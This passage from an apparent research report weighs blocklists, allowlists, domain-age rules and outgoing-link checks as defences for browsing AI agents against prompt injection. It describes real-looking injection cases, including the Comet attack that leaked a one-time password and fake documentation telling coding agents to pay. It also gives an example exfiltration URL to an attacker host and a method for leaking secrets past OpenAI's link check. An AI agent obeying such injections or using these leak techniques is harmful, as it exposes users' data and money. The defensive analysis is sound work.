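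Restricting what the agent can reach while it reads strangers' text would usually be less disruptive than blocking the whole domain. Chaikin and Sahib ask whether a browser needs access to the user's email to summarise a Reddit discussion. If the Comet browser had been unable to open Gmail during the summary, the attacker would have learned the user's email address but not the one-time password.

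## Allowlists, new-domain rules and checks on outgoing links

A blocklist lets an agent open any site that isn't on the list. A developer who finds that too permissive can use an allowlist, which names the only sites the agent may load without further approval. A milder option is to block recently registered domains. Both rules restrict what the agent reads. A developer can also check where the agent sends data or money, which can limit the damage after an injection succeeds.

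### Edge's lists of permitted sites

The October 2025 preview of Edge's agent mode used an allowlist by default. In "Balanced Mode", the agent could open sites on a list that Microsoft had chosen, and it needed the user's approval for any other. In "Strict Mode", it needed approval for every site. According to Microsoft's *Configure browsing with Copilot*, the agent in Edge for Business can open only domains that the company's administrator has authorised, and the feature stays off until the administrator lists some. Microsoft offers a ready-made list of common work sites.

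An allowlist keeps the agent off an attacker's new site from the day it goes up. Nobody has to find the injection first, so cloaking and listing delays don't matter, and nobody has to decide whether borderline text, such as a joke, counts as an attack.

However, Edge compares only the site's origin (such as `https://www.example.com`) and ignores any path, according to Microsoft's *Browsing with Copilot Blocked URLs*. An administrator could allow `example.com` and block `forum.example.com`, but could not allow a shop's product pages and block the reviews on them. An entry also covers subdomains. If an administrator allowed `pages.dev` for its developer documentation, the agent could also open the two sites on Unit 42's list that use `pages.dev` subdomains, one of which contains an instruction to delete files.

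### What a list of popular sites would exclude

An allowlist of the 10,000 most popular domains would exclude most of the sites where Khodayari and colleagues found injections, because those sites were concentrated beyond rank 100,000. It would probably also exclude the 13 sites on Unit 42's list that have their own domains, the 11 domains in Zscaler's two campaigns, and nearly all hacked sites.

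An allowlist of 10,000 hostnames would also exclude almost all harmless sites. Khodayari and colleagues searched 24.8 million hosts in Common Crawl, and 10,000 is 0.04% of that number. Users would notice a much smaller loss, because much of what people asked the Comet agent to do was on a few popular services. The user who wants a vacuum cleaner would still get Amazon and the biggest review sites, but perhaps not the repair shop's blog that explains which models break.

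The benefit also looks smaller when measured in visits. In the invented example from the start of the report, 1,000 of the 11,000 harmful visits were to attackers' own sites, and the rest were to one marketplace. The blocklist prevented 8% of the harmful visits. An allowlist that included the marketplace would prevent all 1,000 visits to attackers' sites, but that is only 9% of the total.

The main gap in an allowlist is therefore malicious posts on permitted sites. In the attack that used a Reddit comment to take over a Perplexity account, Comet visited only Reddit, Perplexity and Gmail, and a typical user would have approved all three. An allowlist is more useful when an attack can't succeed unless the agent visits the attacker's own site. It could have stopped the five WASP attack goals that required such a visit, even if nobody had reported the site.

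A permitted site can also forward the agent elsewhere. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) warns that a link can start on a trusted domain and immediately redirect to an attacker's. As with a blocklist, the software has to check every address in the redirect chain.

### Approving sites that are not on the list

OpenAI's other objection to strict allowlists is that people also visit less popular sites. Frequent warnings about harmless sites can train them to click through without thinking. OpenAI gives no figures for this, and Microsoft hasn't said how often Edge users approve a site.

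Even so, few of these prompts would involve a malicious site. If one in 500 unfamiliar sites is malicious, a user who answers ten prompts a day will meet a malicious site about once in 50 days, after approving hundreds of harmless ones. The prompt also appears before the agent has read the page, so the user has little to go on except the site's name. In Microsoft's example of a related prompt, which appears when a site seems irrelevant to the task, the user is asked whether the agent should continue to Wikipedia.

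*Allow or Block Sites for Browse with Copilot in Microsoft Edge*, a forum tutorial, lists three answers to Edge's prompt to approve a site. "Allow once" is the safest way to approve it, but the prompt appears again next time. "Always allow" ends the prompts, but the approval still applies if an intruder later breaks into the site. "Cancel" stops the action.

In Edge for Business, the administrator decides in advance which sites the agent may use and keeps a blocklist that employees can't change. Microsoft's *Edge for Business presents the world's first secure enterprise AI browser* (2025) recommends starting with a short list of allowed sites. If employees keep requesting more, the administrator can enter an asterisk, which allows every site except those on the blocklist.

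### Letting a model judge the address

A developer could spare users these prompts by having a model decide, but the model may be unreliable. In the MalURLBench test, disguised malicious addresses often fooled older models.

Kong and colleagues built 61,845 test cases around ten everyday tasks, such as tracking a parcel or finding a restaurant that delivers. They told each model to watch for attacks, then gave it a web address and asked whether it would visit. In one small trial, Llama 3 8B accepted a malicious address 15% of the time, and 20% when a sentence beside the address called it official. When similar words appeared inside the address, the model accepted it 60% or 75% of the time, depending on where the words were.

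The models seemed to trust descriptions written into an address. Addresses that contained phrases such as "this is a popular food delivery service" succeeded 71.5% of the time, compared with 60.9% for addresses that contained a well-known site's name. Models also accepted some newer domain endings, such as .art and .link, more often than .com.

These rates probably overstate the danger on the open web. When a disguise rarely fooled a model, the team rewrote it and kept the versions that worked better. The address also came from the agent's own user, whereas an injection would supply it through a web page, which a model may trust less.

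These disguises don't affect an ordinary blocklist lookup. They changed only the subdomain, path and query, so an entry for the registrable domain would match every version. The malicious sites came from public lists, so an agent that checked those lists first would presumably have rejected most of the addresses before a model had to judge them.

Kong and colleagues built a filter called URLGuard for addresses that no list includes. They trained Llama 2 7B, a small model from 2023, on 140 malicious and 140 normal addresses. All the malicious examples came from the shopping task, and they tested the filter on the other nine tasks. Acceptance of malicious addresses fell by 81 percentage points on average and reached zero in several tasks, but the filter still accepted 61% of them for music recommendations and 70% for weather.

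The results cover only malicious addresses, so they don't show how many harmless ones URLGuard would reject. A filter that rejected every address would have scored better. Before replacing approval prompts with a filter like URLGuard, a developer would need to test it on the small shops and blogs that agents visit.

### Refusing recently registered domains

Checking a domain's age is simpler than having a model assess the domain. A rule against new domains covers a real weakness of blocklists, the period before they can react. *DarkDNS* (2024) identified 42,358 domains that disappeared so soon after registration that they never appeared in the regular snapshots of registered names. Two large registrars told the researchers that such domains are most likely malicious, yet blocklists flagged only 5% of them, and 94% of those entries came after the domain had disappeared.

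The study also allows a rough estimate of how many harmless domains the rule would block. It found 555,491 new domains that were deleted before February 2024, about 10% of all the new domains it detected. Only 6.6% of the deleted domains were on a blocklist. If every deleted domain had been malicious and every surviving one harmless, about nine in ten of the domains blocked by the rule would have been harmless. The true share is uncertain because some harmless domains were deleted and some malicious ones survived.

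How many malicious pages the rule would catch depends on how attackers get their domains. The table applies a 30-day rule to evidence from earlier sections.

| Evidence | What a 30-day rule would do |
|---|---|
| Half of the phishing domains that attackers seemed to have bought were on a blocklist within 16.3 days of registration | Cover the whole wait for at least half |
| The median self-hosted phishing site was on a domain 71 days old | Miss at least half |
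| The median phishing site on a free website builder was on a domain 13.7 years old | Miss at least half, and probably nearly all |
| At least 59% of the pages with injections in October 2025 already had one a year earlier | Miss at least 59% |

The last row consists mostly of pranks, protests and promotion, so sites hosting actual attacks might be younger. But the figure shows that a site's age is a poor clue to whether it contains an injection.

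A new-domain rule works very well against one unusual danger, links to unregistered domains. Some large companies' llms.txt files contained such links. If an attacker registered one of those domains and an agent followed the link the next day, the rule would block the visit.

Many honest sites are also new, especially just after a major event. *A First Look at COVID-19 Domain Names* (2021) warns that treating every pandemic-themed domain as malicious could block information that people needed. It is therefore safer to combine a domain's age with other clues. *INFERMAL* (2025), a study of malicious registrations, gives the example of a one-day-old domain containing "chase", the name of a bank. A site built to inject instructions needn't imitate a bank, so that combination would often miss it.

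Hosting is a more promising clue, because attackers tend to reuse servers. *MANTIS* (Deniz, Nabeel and colleagues, 2025) describes a system that examines new domains on servers with a bad record. The system caught 86.9% of malicious domains, often days or weeks before popular blocklists listed them, and wrongly flagged 0.1% of harmless ones. The paper also reports that 99.7% of flagged domains were malicious, but that figure depends on how common malicious domains are in the test data. The three figures are consistent if roughly a quarter of the tested domains were malicious.

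If only one in 500 domains were malicious, as in the earlier examples, the system would flag 869 malicious domains and 499 harmless ones out of every 500,000, so about 64% of the flagged domains would be malicious. That is much better than blocking every new domain, but an agent would still lose access to some harmless sites. The system would also work only against injection sites whose owners use the same servers as other criminals.

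An attacker can defeat an age rule by waiting. PhishTime let its test domains age for six months, and an attacker could do the same for the price of a registration. They could also buy a domain whose owner no longer wants it. If they buy it before the registry deletes it, the domain keeps its old creation date and probably its links from other sites. After deletion, a new registration normally resets the date, so the age rule applies again.

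### OpenAI's check on outgoing links

An agent can leak information just by requesting a page. Suppose an injection tells it to open this address, with the user's email address in place of the last word:

`https://attacker.example/collect?data=email`

The attacker then reads the email address in the server's log. The page needn't contain anything, and the user may not notice, because an agent can make the request in the background while it loads an image or previews a link. OpenAI's safeguard, which it described in January 2026, works as follows:

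1. A crawler with no access to users' conversations or accounts scans the public web and records the addresses it finds.
2. Before the agent loads an address automatically, software looks for that exact address in the crawler's records.
3. If the address is there, the agent loads it.
4. If it isn't, the software either tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning with the address in it.

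According to *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on the security research blog Embrace The Red, an address the user types into the chat seems to count as safe for the rest of the session.

The crawler is very unlikely to have recorded an address that contains the user's private data, because that data isn't on the public web. The check therefore works on the first day of an attack, whatever the domain's reputation. It should also stop attempts to send the data through a redirect on a trusted site, since the redirect's address would contain the same data.

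OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak a user's data through a URL it loads. It says the check doesn't make a page's content trustworthy or keep out harmful instructions. An attacker's page passes the check once the crawler has recorded it, so the check would barely change the share of harmful visits that agents avoid. It also wouldn't have stopped the attack on Comet, in which the agent posted the stolen password as a Reddit comment.

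Small amounts of data can still leak through allowed addresses. Embrace The Red describes an attacker who owns 36 public pages, one for each letter and digit, and tells the agent to open them in an order that spells out a secret. Each request passes because the address is in the crawler's records. A six-digit login code would take six visits, or two if the attacker had 1,000 pages that each stood for three digits.

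Browsers make this harder because they might not request the same page twice, and requests can arrive out of order. The blog Embrace The Red suggests going further by preventing the agent from opening any address more than once in a session. It also points out that a safeguard protects only the products that use it, and that OpenAI's earlier version was once missing from its Mac and iPhone apps.

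The drawback is more warnings. The crawler may have no record of a page published this morning or of a shop's results for an unusual search. If the agent can't find a substitute, the user sees a warning, and repeated warnings bring back the habit of clicking through that OpenAI wants to avoid.

### Payments through Stripe and PayPal

Checking where money goes is harder than checking where data goes. Unit 42 published three payment addresses from the injections it found, two on Stripe and one on PayPal. Both services also handle payments for many honest businesses.

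| Site with the injection | Where the agent should pay | Narrowest useful entry |
|---|---|---|
| Library of 3D models | A Stripe payment link | The link's full address |
| Running-shoe site | Probably the other Stripe link | The link's full address |
| Two sites with a $5,000 payment order | One PayPal page | The page's full address |
| Subscription page on free hosting | The service's own domain, after a Google login | That domain |

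A domain blocklist could stop only the final payment, by blocking its destination. But blocking Stripe or PayPal would also prevent the agent from buying a vacuum cleaner from many ordinary shops. An allowlist for shopping would include both domains, and a new-domain rule wouldn't block them because neither is new. OpenAI's check wouldn't help either, because a payment link contains no private data about the user.

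A blocklist entry for a payment page's full address would block it without affecting other sellers, and one entry would cover both sites that used the PayPal page. Safe Browsing's format allows such entries, but Edge's business lists don't, because they ignore the path. The attacker could open another account, though that may take longer than registering a domain. Stripe and PayPal can do more than any list by closing the attacker's account, which protects people as well as agents.

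Checking the domains of outgoing links does not stop payments to a cryptocurrency wallet, which has no domain. The fake Python documentation contained instructions for coding agents to send $3 to a wallet, and an agent that controls its own funds could do so without opening another page.

Asking the user to confirm a payment avoids having to judge the address. Microsoft says in *New in Edge for Business* (2026) that its agent pauses for the user when a page needs a password or card number, and the consumer version asks for supervision before buying an item. Such prompts are rarer than prompts about unfamiliar sites, and they can be much more informative if they show the amount and the recipient. Few people would approve sending $5,000 to a stranger while shopping for a vacuum cleaner. But someone who had asked for running shoes might well approve the $45 pair on the site Unit 42 found, and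 a programmer might approve a $3 licence that appeared to fix an error.

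## How much exposure a blocklist would remove, and how attackers would respond

Nobody has measured what share of browsing agents' harmful visits a blocklist would prevent. Phishing figures allow a rough estimate, but it requires guessing how harmful visits divide among different kinds of site, so it is worth checking how much the estimate changes with different guesses.

### Adding up the hosting routes

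An attacker can put an injection on a domain they own, on free hosting, in a post on a trusted site, or on a hacked site. Three quantities determine how much a blocklist removes on each route:

- w, the route's share of all harmful visits by agents
- c, the list's coverage of malicious pages on that route
- f, the share of visits to the listed pages that come after listing

Multiplying the three for each route and adding the results gives the share of all harmful visits removed.

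For a 21-hour campaign with steady traffic, the FreePhish figures imply that Safe Browsing blocks about 71% of visits to attackers' own domains (74.2% coverage and a 51-minute delay) and 13% of visits to their pages on free hosting. The estimate is zero for posts on trusted sites and for hacked sites, because blocking those domains would also block their legitimate content.

Suppose that 60% of harmful visits are to attackers' own domains, 20% to free hosting, and 20% to trusted or hacked sites. Suppose also that attackers respond to the blocklist by moving, until the shares are 10%, 40%, and 50%.

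| Where the injection is | Visits blocked on this route | Share before the move | Points removed | Share after the move | Points removed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Attackers' own domains | 71.2% | 60% | 42.7 | 10% | 7.1 |
| Free hosting | 13.1% | 20% | 2.6 | 40% | 5.3 |
| Trusted or hacked sites | 0% | 20% | 0 | 50% | 0 |
| Total | | 100% | 45.3 | 100% | 12.4 |

The filter removes about 45% of harmful visits before attackers shift toward trusted sites and 12% afterward, although the list is equally good in both cases. For every 10 percentage points of harmful visits that move from attackers' own domains to trusted sites, the share the filter removes falls by about seven points.

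Both totals assume that every agent checks the list. Several products showed no sign of doing so in the tests with phishing pages. If half of all harmful visits came from agents that don't check the list, both totals would halve.

### Changing the assumed shares

For phishing, Oest and colleagues provide a partial record of where visits went. They list the domain type and the number of visits by identifiable customers for the 20 largest campaigns in their data. Eight campaigns used hacked sites and received 46% of the visits, nine used domains registered by attackers (37%), and three used free subdomains (17%). With these shares, the filter would remove 28% of harmful visits.

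Free subdomains made up only 0.79% of the phishing addresses in that study, so counting addresses would have made them look negligible. But the 20 campaigns received just 24% of the recorded visits, and all 20 targeted customers of one financial company. The campaigns may also have grown so large because they used sites that blocklist operators are reluctant to block.

| Attackers' own domains | Free hosting | Trusted or hacked sites | Source of the shares | Harmful visits removed |
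|---|---|---|---|---|
| 80% | 10% | 10% | Assumed | 58% |
| 60% | 20% | 20% | Assumed | 45% |
| 37% | 17% | 46% | 20 largest phishing campaigns | 28% |
| 10% | 40% | 50% | Assumed | 12% |
| 9% | 0% | 91% | Invented marketplace example | 6% |

The last row uses the invented marketplace from the start of the report. It may be closer to what a shopping agent encounters than the first two rows, because such agents spend much of their time on large shopping sites.

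Assuming the list blocks no hacked sites is too pessimistic, since browsers do block some of them. If the list stopped half of the visits to hacked sites in the third row, the total would rise from 28% to 51%, but agents would also lose access to the site owners' legitimate pages.

### Changing coverage and timing

The 74.2% coverage figure dates from 2022 and 2023. Kaur and colleagues got much lower figures in October 2026. Whenever their automated investigator found a new scam site, they opened it in Chrome with enhanced protection switched on. Chrome already blocked 44.1% of the sites that tried to steal login details but only 7.9% of the other scam sites. Microsoft's SmartScreen blocked 41.6% and 7.3%, respectively.

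The team reported every site to the blocklist operators at once and kept checking for a week. These are some of the results for Safe Browsing:

| Type of scam | Sites | Blocked when found | Blocked within a week | Median wait for sites blocked later |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Bank or card company impersonation | 374 | 44.1% | 69.8% | 30 hours |
| Tech support | 161 | 34.2% | 58.4% | 43 hours |
| Investment | 473 | 13.3% | 29.0% | 78 hours |
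| Online purchase | 793 | 12.5% | 26.7% | 96 hours |
| Home improvement | 83 | 4.8% | 12.0% | 142 hours |

The fake Python documentation, which sold a worthless licence, most resembles the online-purchase scams. If Safe Browsing treated attackers' injection sites like those scams, it would block about 12.5% of visits to a 21-hour campaign, because most later blocklist entries would come after the campaign had ended. The overall estimate would fall from 45% to 10%. Even 10% may be too high, because a page that attacks only agents can look harmless to a scam detector.

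The next table varies one input at a time, for both sets of assumed shares.

| Change | Before attackers move | After attackers move |
|---|---|---|
| None | 45% | 12% |
| Pages stay up for a year instead of 21 hours | 48% | 15% |
| Coverage is 83% for own domains and 31% for free hosting | 52% | 17% |
| Only 37% of visits come after listing | 18% | 6% |
| The list treats attackers' own domains like online-purchase scams | 10% | 7% |
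| The list catches all of attackers' own domains immediately | 63% | 15% |

The second row matters because many injections last far longer than phishing pages. This helps the filter only slightly when listing is fast, because a 51-minute delay was already short compared with 21 hours, but it helps more when listing is slow. If pages stayed up for a year and the list eventually included 26.7% of attackers' own domains, as with online-purchase scams, the total before the move would be about 20% instead of 10%.

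The coverage figures in the third row come from *A Large-Scale Analysis of Phishing Websites Hosted on Free Web Hosting Domains*, which describes the same FreePhish data. The paper reports them as Safe Browsing's coverage after 24 hours, but they are higher than Safe Browsing's totals for a whole week. The paper doesn't explain the discrepancy.

The 37% in the fourth row is roughly the share of phishing victims in Oest and colleagues' data who arrived after detection. It is a pessimistic choice because detection took about nine hours. But agents could arrive as early as those victims did if a new listing appeared on a busy shopping page.

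Before attackers move to other sites, the share of exposure a blocklist removes depends most on how well it covers the attackers' own domains. In the table, varying that coverage alone raises the estimate from 10% to 63%. After attackers move, even perfect coverage of those domains would remove only 15%, so the attackers' choice of site matters more than any improvement the list's operator can make.

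### Would the blocked attacks have worked?

Blocking an injection achieves little if the model would have ignored it. In 5,200 summarising trials by Khodayari and colleagues, small models followed injections most often. The researchers read every answer to check whether it followed the injection.

| Type of model | Models | Trials | Injections followed | Rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Small, open | 3 | 1,200 | 50 | 4.2% |
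| Medium, open | 5 | 2,000 | 12 | 0.6% |
| Large, open | 3 | 1,200 | 14 | 1.2% |
| Closed | 2 | 800 | 5 | 0.6% |

On plain text, small models followed 8.0% of injections, compared with 2.4% to 3.4% for the other three groups. The published figures imply that all five failures by closed models were on plain text. A developer who uses a strong model but strips pages down to text therefore loses some of the model's protection.

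A blocklist prevents more successful injections when the model is more likely to follow them. In 10,000 harmful visits, a model that followed 0.6% of injections would follow 60, and a filter that blocked 45% of the visits at random would prevent 27 of those. With a small model reading plain text, the same filter would prevent about 360. If attackers moved as assumed above, the filter would prevent about seven in the first case and 99 in the second.

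These rates measure how often models followed the injections, not how much harm resulted. The injections came from a collection of mostly pranks, protests and promotion, so following one might only mean answering in German. The closed group contained only two models.

The trials do support one criticism of blocklists, that a list built by searching for phrases such as "ignore all previous instructions" will mostly block attacks that strong models nearly always ignore.

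The fake Python documentation shows that this isn't true of every attack a domain list could block. Zscaler gave its test agent a payment tool and no spending limit, and four of 26 models paid, including Gemini 2.5 Pro, which is not a small model. The other three were Llama 3.3 70B, Llama 3.2 90B Vision and Gemini 3 Flash.

The fake DeBank site fooled fewer models. None of the 26 accepted it as genuine when they also had the official site. Without the official site, GPT-5.4 accepted it when it appeared alongside other sources, and Claude Sonnet 4.5 accepted it when it was the only source. Newer models may do better. Zscaler counted models but didn't report a success rate over repeated attempts, so "four out of 26" doesn't mean that 15% of such attacks succeed.

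An attacker who owns a site can make the whole page support the injection, with a believable error message, matching metadata and a payment form, while one who posts a comment has only a few lines and no control over the surrounding text. But readers may trust a comment more because it appears on a familiar site. Nobody has tested the same models on comparable attacks in both places.

The estimate could change considerably if injections succeed more often on some kinds of site than on others. Suppose a model obeyed 0.6% of injections on attackers' own domains and free hosting, and 6% of those on trusted or hacked sites. With the original 60%, 20% and 20% shares, the filter would still remove 45% of harmful visits, but only 16% of successful attacks. If injections on attackers' own domains and free hosting were instead twice as likely to succeed as the others, it would remove 50% of successful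 attacks.

### Where spammers went after a crackdown

The assumption that attackers would move to free hosting and trusted sites needs some support, since attackers don't always respond to a new defence. Email spam provides the clearest evidence that they can respond.

For much of 2007 and 2008, anyone could register a .cn domain for one yuan, about 10 to 15 US cents. Spammers bought these domains in bulk and discarded them once they were blocklisted. In December 2009, the Chinese registry began to require paper documents, and the lowest price rose to 69 yuan, about $10. Liu, Levchenko and colleagues (2011) studied the effects of these changes in *On the Effects of Registrar-level Intervention*, using registration records and several collections of spam.

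Spammers stopped registering Chinese .cn domains almost immediately. From mid-January 2010, they were registering Russian .ru domains about as fast as they had registered .cn ones. Their stock of cheap .cn domains lasted another six weeks. Then, within a week, they replaced .cn with .ru in their messages, and the total amount of spam did not change.

A narrower measure in 2010 had a similar result. The large registrar eNom agreed to shut down the domains of illegal online pharmacies, and Liu and colleagues found that the business moved elsewhere without shrinking much.

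Phishers have moved in the opposite direction more recently. The company Freenom used to give away domains under several country endings, including .tk. Lim and colleagues found that phishers' use of .cn increased after Freenom stopped.

In all three cases, the attackers moved to other domains that a blocklist could still include. The operator then has to find the new sites, but the attacks still arrive by the same route. The fall from 45% to 12% would happen only if attackers gave up most of their own domains for places where blocking works badly or not at all, and none of these studies shows that happening.

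The share of phishing attacks on free and cheap subdomain services fell from 24% in 2023–24 to 7% in May to July 2026, even though Safe Browsing has been much worse at catching pages on free hosting. Hosting companies can remove pages, and attackers may find it easier to buy domains in bulk.

Attackers who use prompt injection have more reason to move to large sites than phishers do. An injection needs only a sentence, which fits in a product review, whereas phishing normally needs a page that looks like a login form. Many agents also already visit large shops and forums. The attacker behind the fake Python documentation could have moved the instructions into the ten linked GitHub repositories within a few minutes, and blocking the scam domains would then have made no difference. The shares of 10%, 40% and 50% are therefore a plausible bad case, but not a forecast.

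### What a replacement costs

An attacker whose domain is on a blocklist can buy another cheaply. *INFERMAL* collected the prices on offer when criminals registered 14,474 domains for phishing. The prices ranged from $0.78 to $69, and nearly half of the domains cost $2 or less. Replacing a $2 domain every day would cost $730 a year. At least some phishers will pay more for a convincing name, such as usps.bar, the most expensive domain in the study.

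Small price differences still seem to matter to bulk buyers. In the study's statistical model, each dollar off the price was associated with 49% more malicious registrations. Free extras such as web hosting were associated with 88% more, and strict registration rules with 63% fewer. These are correlations, and the hosting result is weak because free hosting was available for only 254 of the domains.

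Buying many domains also takes work. *Spam, Domain Names and Registrars* notes that spammers who must use large numbers of domains may need software to create and manage them. This work is easy to automate if the registrar lets customers' programs open accounts or register domains. *INFERMAL* associates such access with 401% more malicious registrations.

Whether a $2 replacement domain is worth buying depends on how much the injection earns. If an agent obeyed 0.6% of injections, a page that asked for $3 would need about 111 visits to recover the price of the domain. At an 8% success rate, it would need nine. A page that asked for $5,000 would earn an average of $30 per visit even at the lower rate, enough to justify the purchase with a single visit. A blocklist can therefore make small frauds unprofitable if it blocks each domain early enough, but the price of domains won't deter attackers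 seeking large payments.

Attackers can replace free hosting without spending anything, and the same is true of a comment on a trusted site unless the account took effort to establish. *INFERMAL* doesn't cover old domains or hacked sites, but an attacker can get an old domain by registering a cheap one and waiting, and an AI search for WordPress flaws to exploit can cost about $25.

### Why replacing a domain can cost an attacker visitors

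A phisher who loses a domain can send new messages with a new address, so the replacement has visitors immediately. An injection that depends on search results is harder to move to a new domain, because that domain has no ranking and few links, and an agent looking for help with a Python package is unlikely to find it. Blocklists are therefore more useful against these injections than the low price of domains suggests.

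Suppose an established scam page receives 100 agent visits a day. Once a blocklist adds the page, the attacker opens a new site, whose traffic climbs steadily from zero to 100 visits a day over 30 days. If the blocklist catches each new site after ten days, that site will have received about 170 visits, compared with 1,000 for an established page in the same time. The attacker loses 83% of the traffic even though the list is slow, and the new site never reaches the original's ranking. These numbers are invented, but the same thing happens whenever traffic builds more slowly than the list is updated.

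*INFERMAL* found that how quickly registrars took down phishing domains had little effect on how many such domains criminals registered, probably because a phishing page can collect passwords in a very short time. This finding may not carry over to prompt injection pages that have to wait for search traffic, since early removal or blocking would hurt them much more.

Pages that agents can find through search are also easier for defenders to find. Google had indexed only 4.1% of the 25,200 older free-hosted phishing addresses in *A Large-Scale Analysis of Phishing Websites Hosted on Free Web Hosting Domains*, and 44.7% contained a tag meant to keep them out of search results. Phishers can hide from search engines because they send people links. Attackers who rely on agents' searches have to let at least the search engine's crawler see the page. They could use cloaking to show the crawler a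 clean version, but that version would still need the search terms that attract agents.

An attacker who controls the links to a blocked domain can keep some of its traffic by pointing them to a new domain. The owner of the ten GitHub repositories could have redirected visitors immediately by editing the address. Comments on busy forums could send visitors to the new domain too. A blocklist operator who also reported the repositories to GitHub would make the next replacement domain harder for visitors to find.

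### One entry for every agent

A blocklist entry protects every agent that checks the list, including agents with small or outdated models, so each entry is more useful when more agents share the list. If a page fools one company's agent, listing that page could protect other companies' agents the next day, before their developers have trained a new model or even heard of the attack.

Finding scam sites may also become cheaper. Kaur and colleagues ran their investigator on two workstations, using two small models with about four billion parameters each. In 28 days it examined 552,809 accessible websites and flagged 4,054, of which 12 turned out to be harmless. The team later checked 2,000 sites that the investigator had passed and found one scam. On an earlier test set, the median investigation took 44 seconds.

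The system looked for scams aimed at people, so it would need new training to recognise injections, and it would have to resist instructions on the pages it investigated. But the same approach could raise coverage of attackers' own domains, and that coverage has the largest effect on the estimate as long as attackers keep using those domains. In its live run, the system found sites through certificate logs, which don't show new posts on trusted sites or most new pages on free hosting.

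The automated rewriting that worked well in the MUZZLE tests wouldn't help an attacker reach an agent that refuses to load the domain. A blocklist can also stop attacks that the model may fail to resist, such as the one in which Gemini 2.5 Pro agreed to buy a $3 licence.
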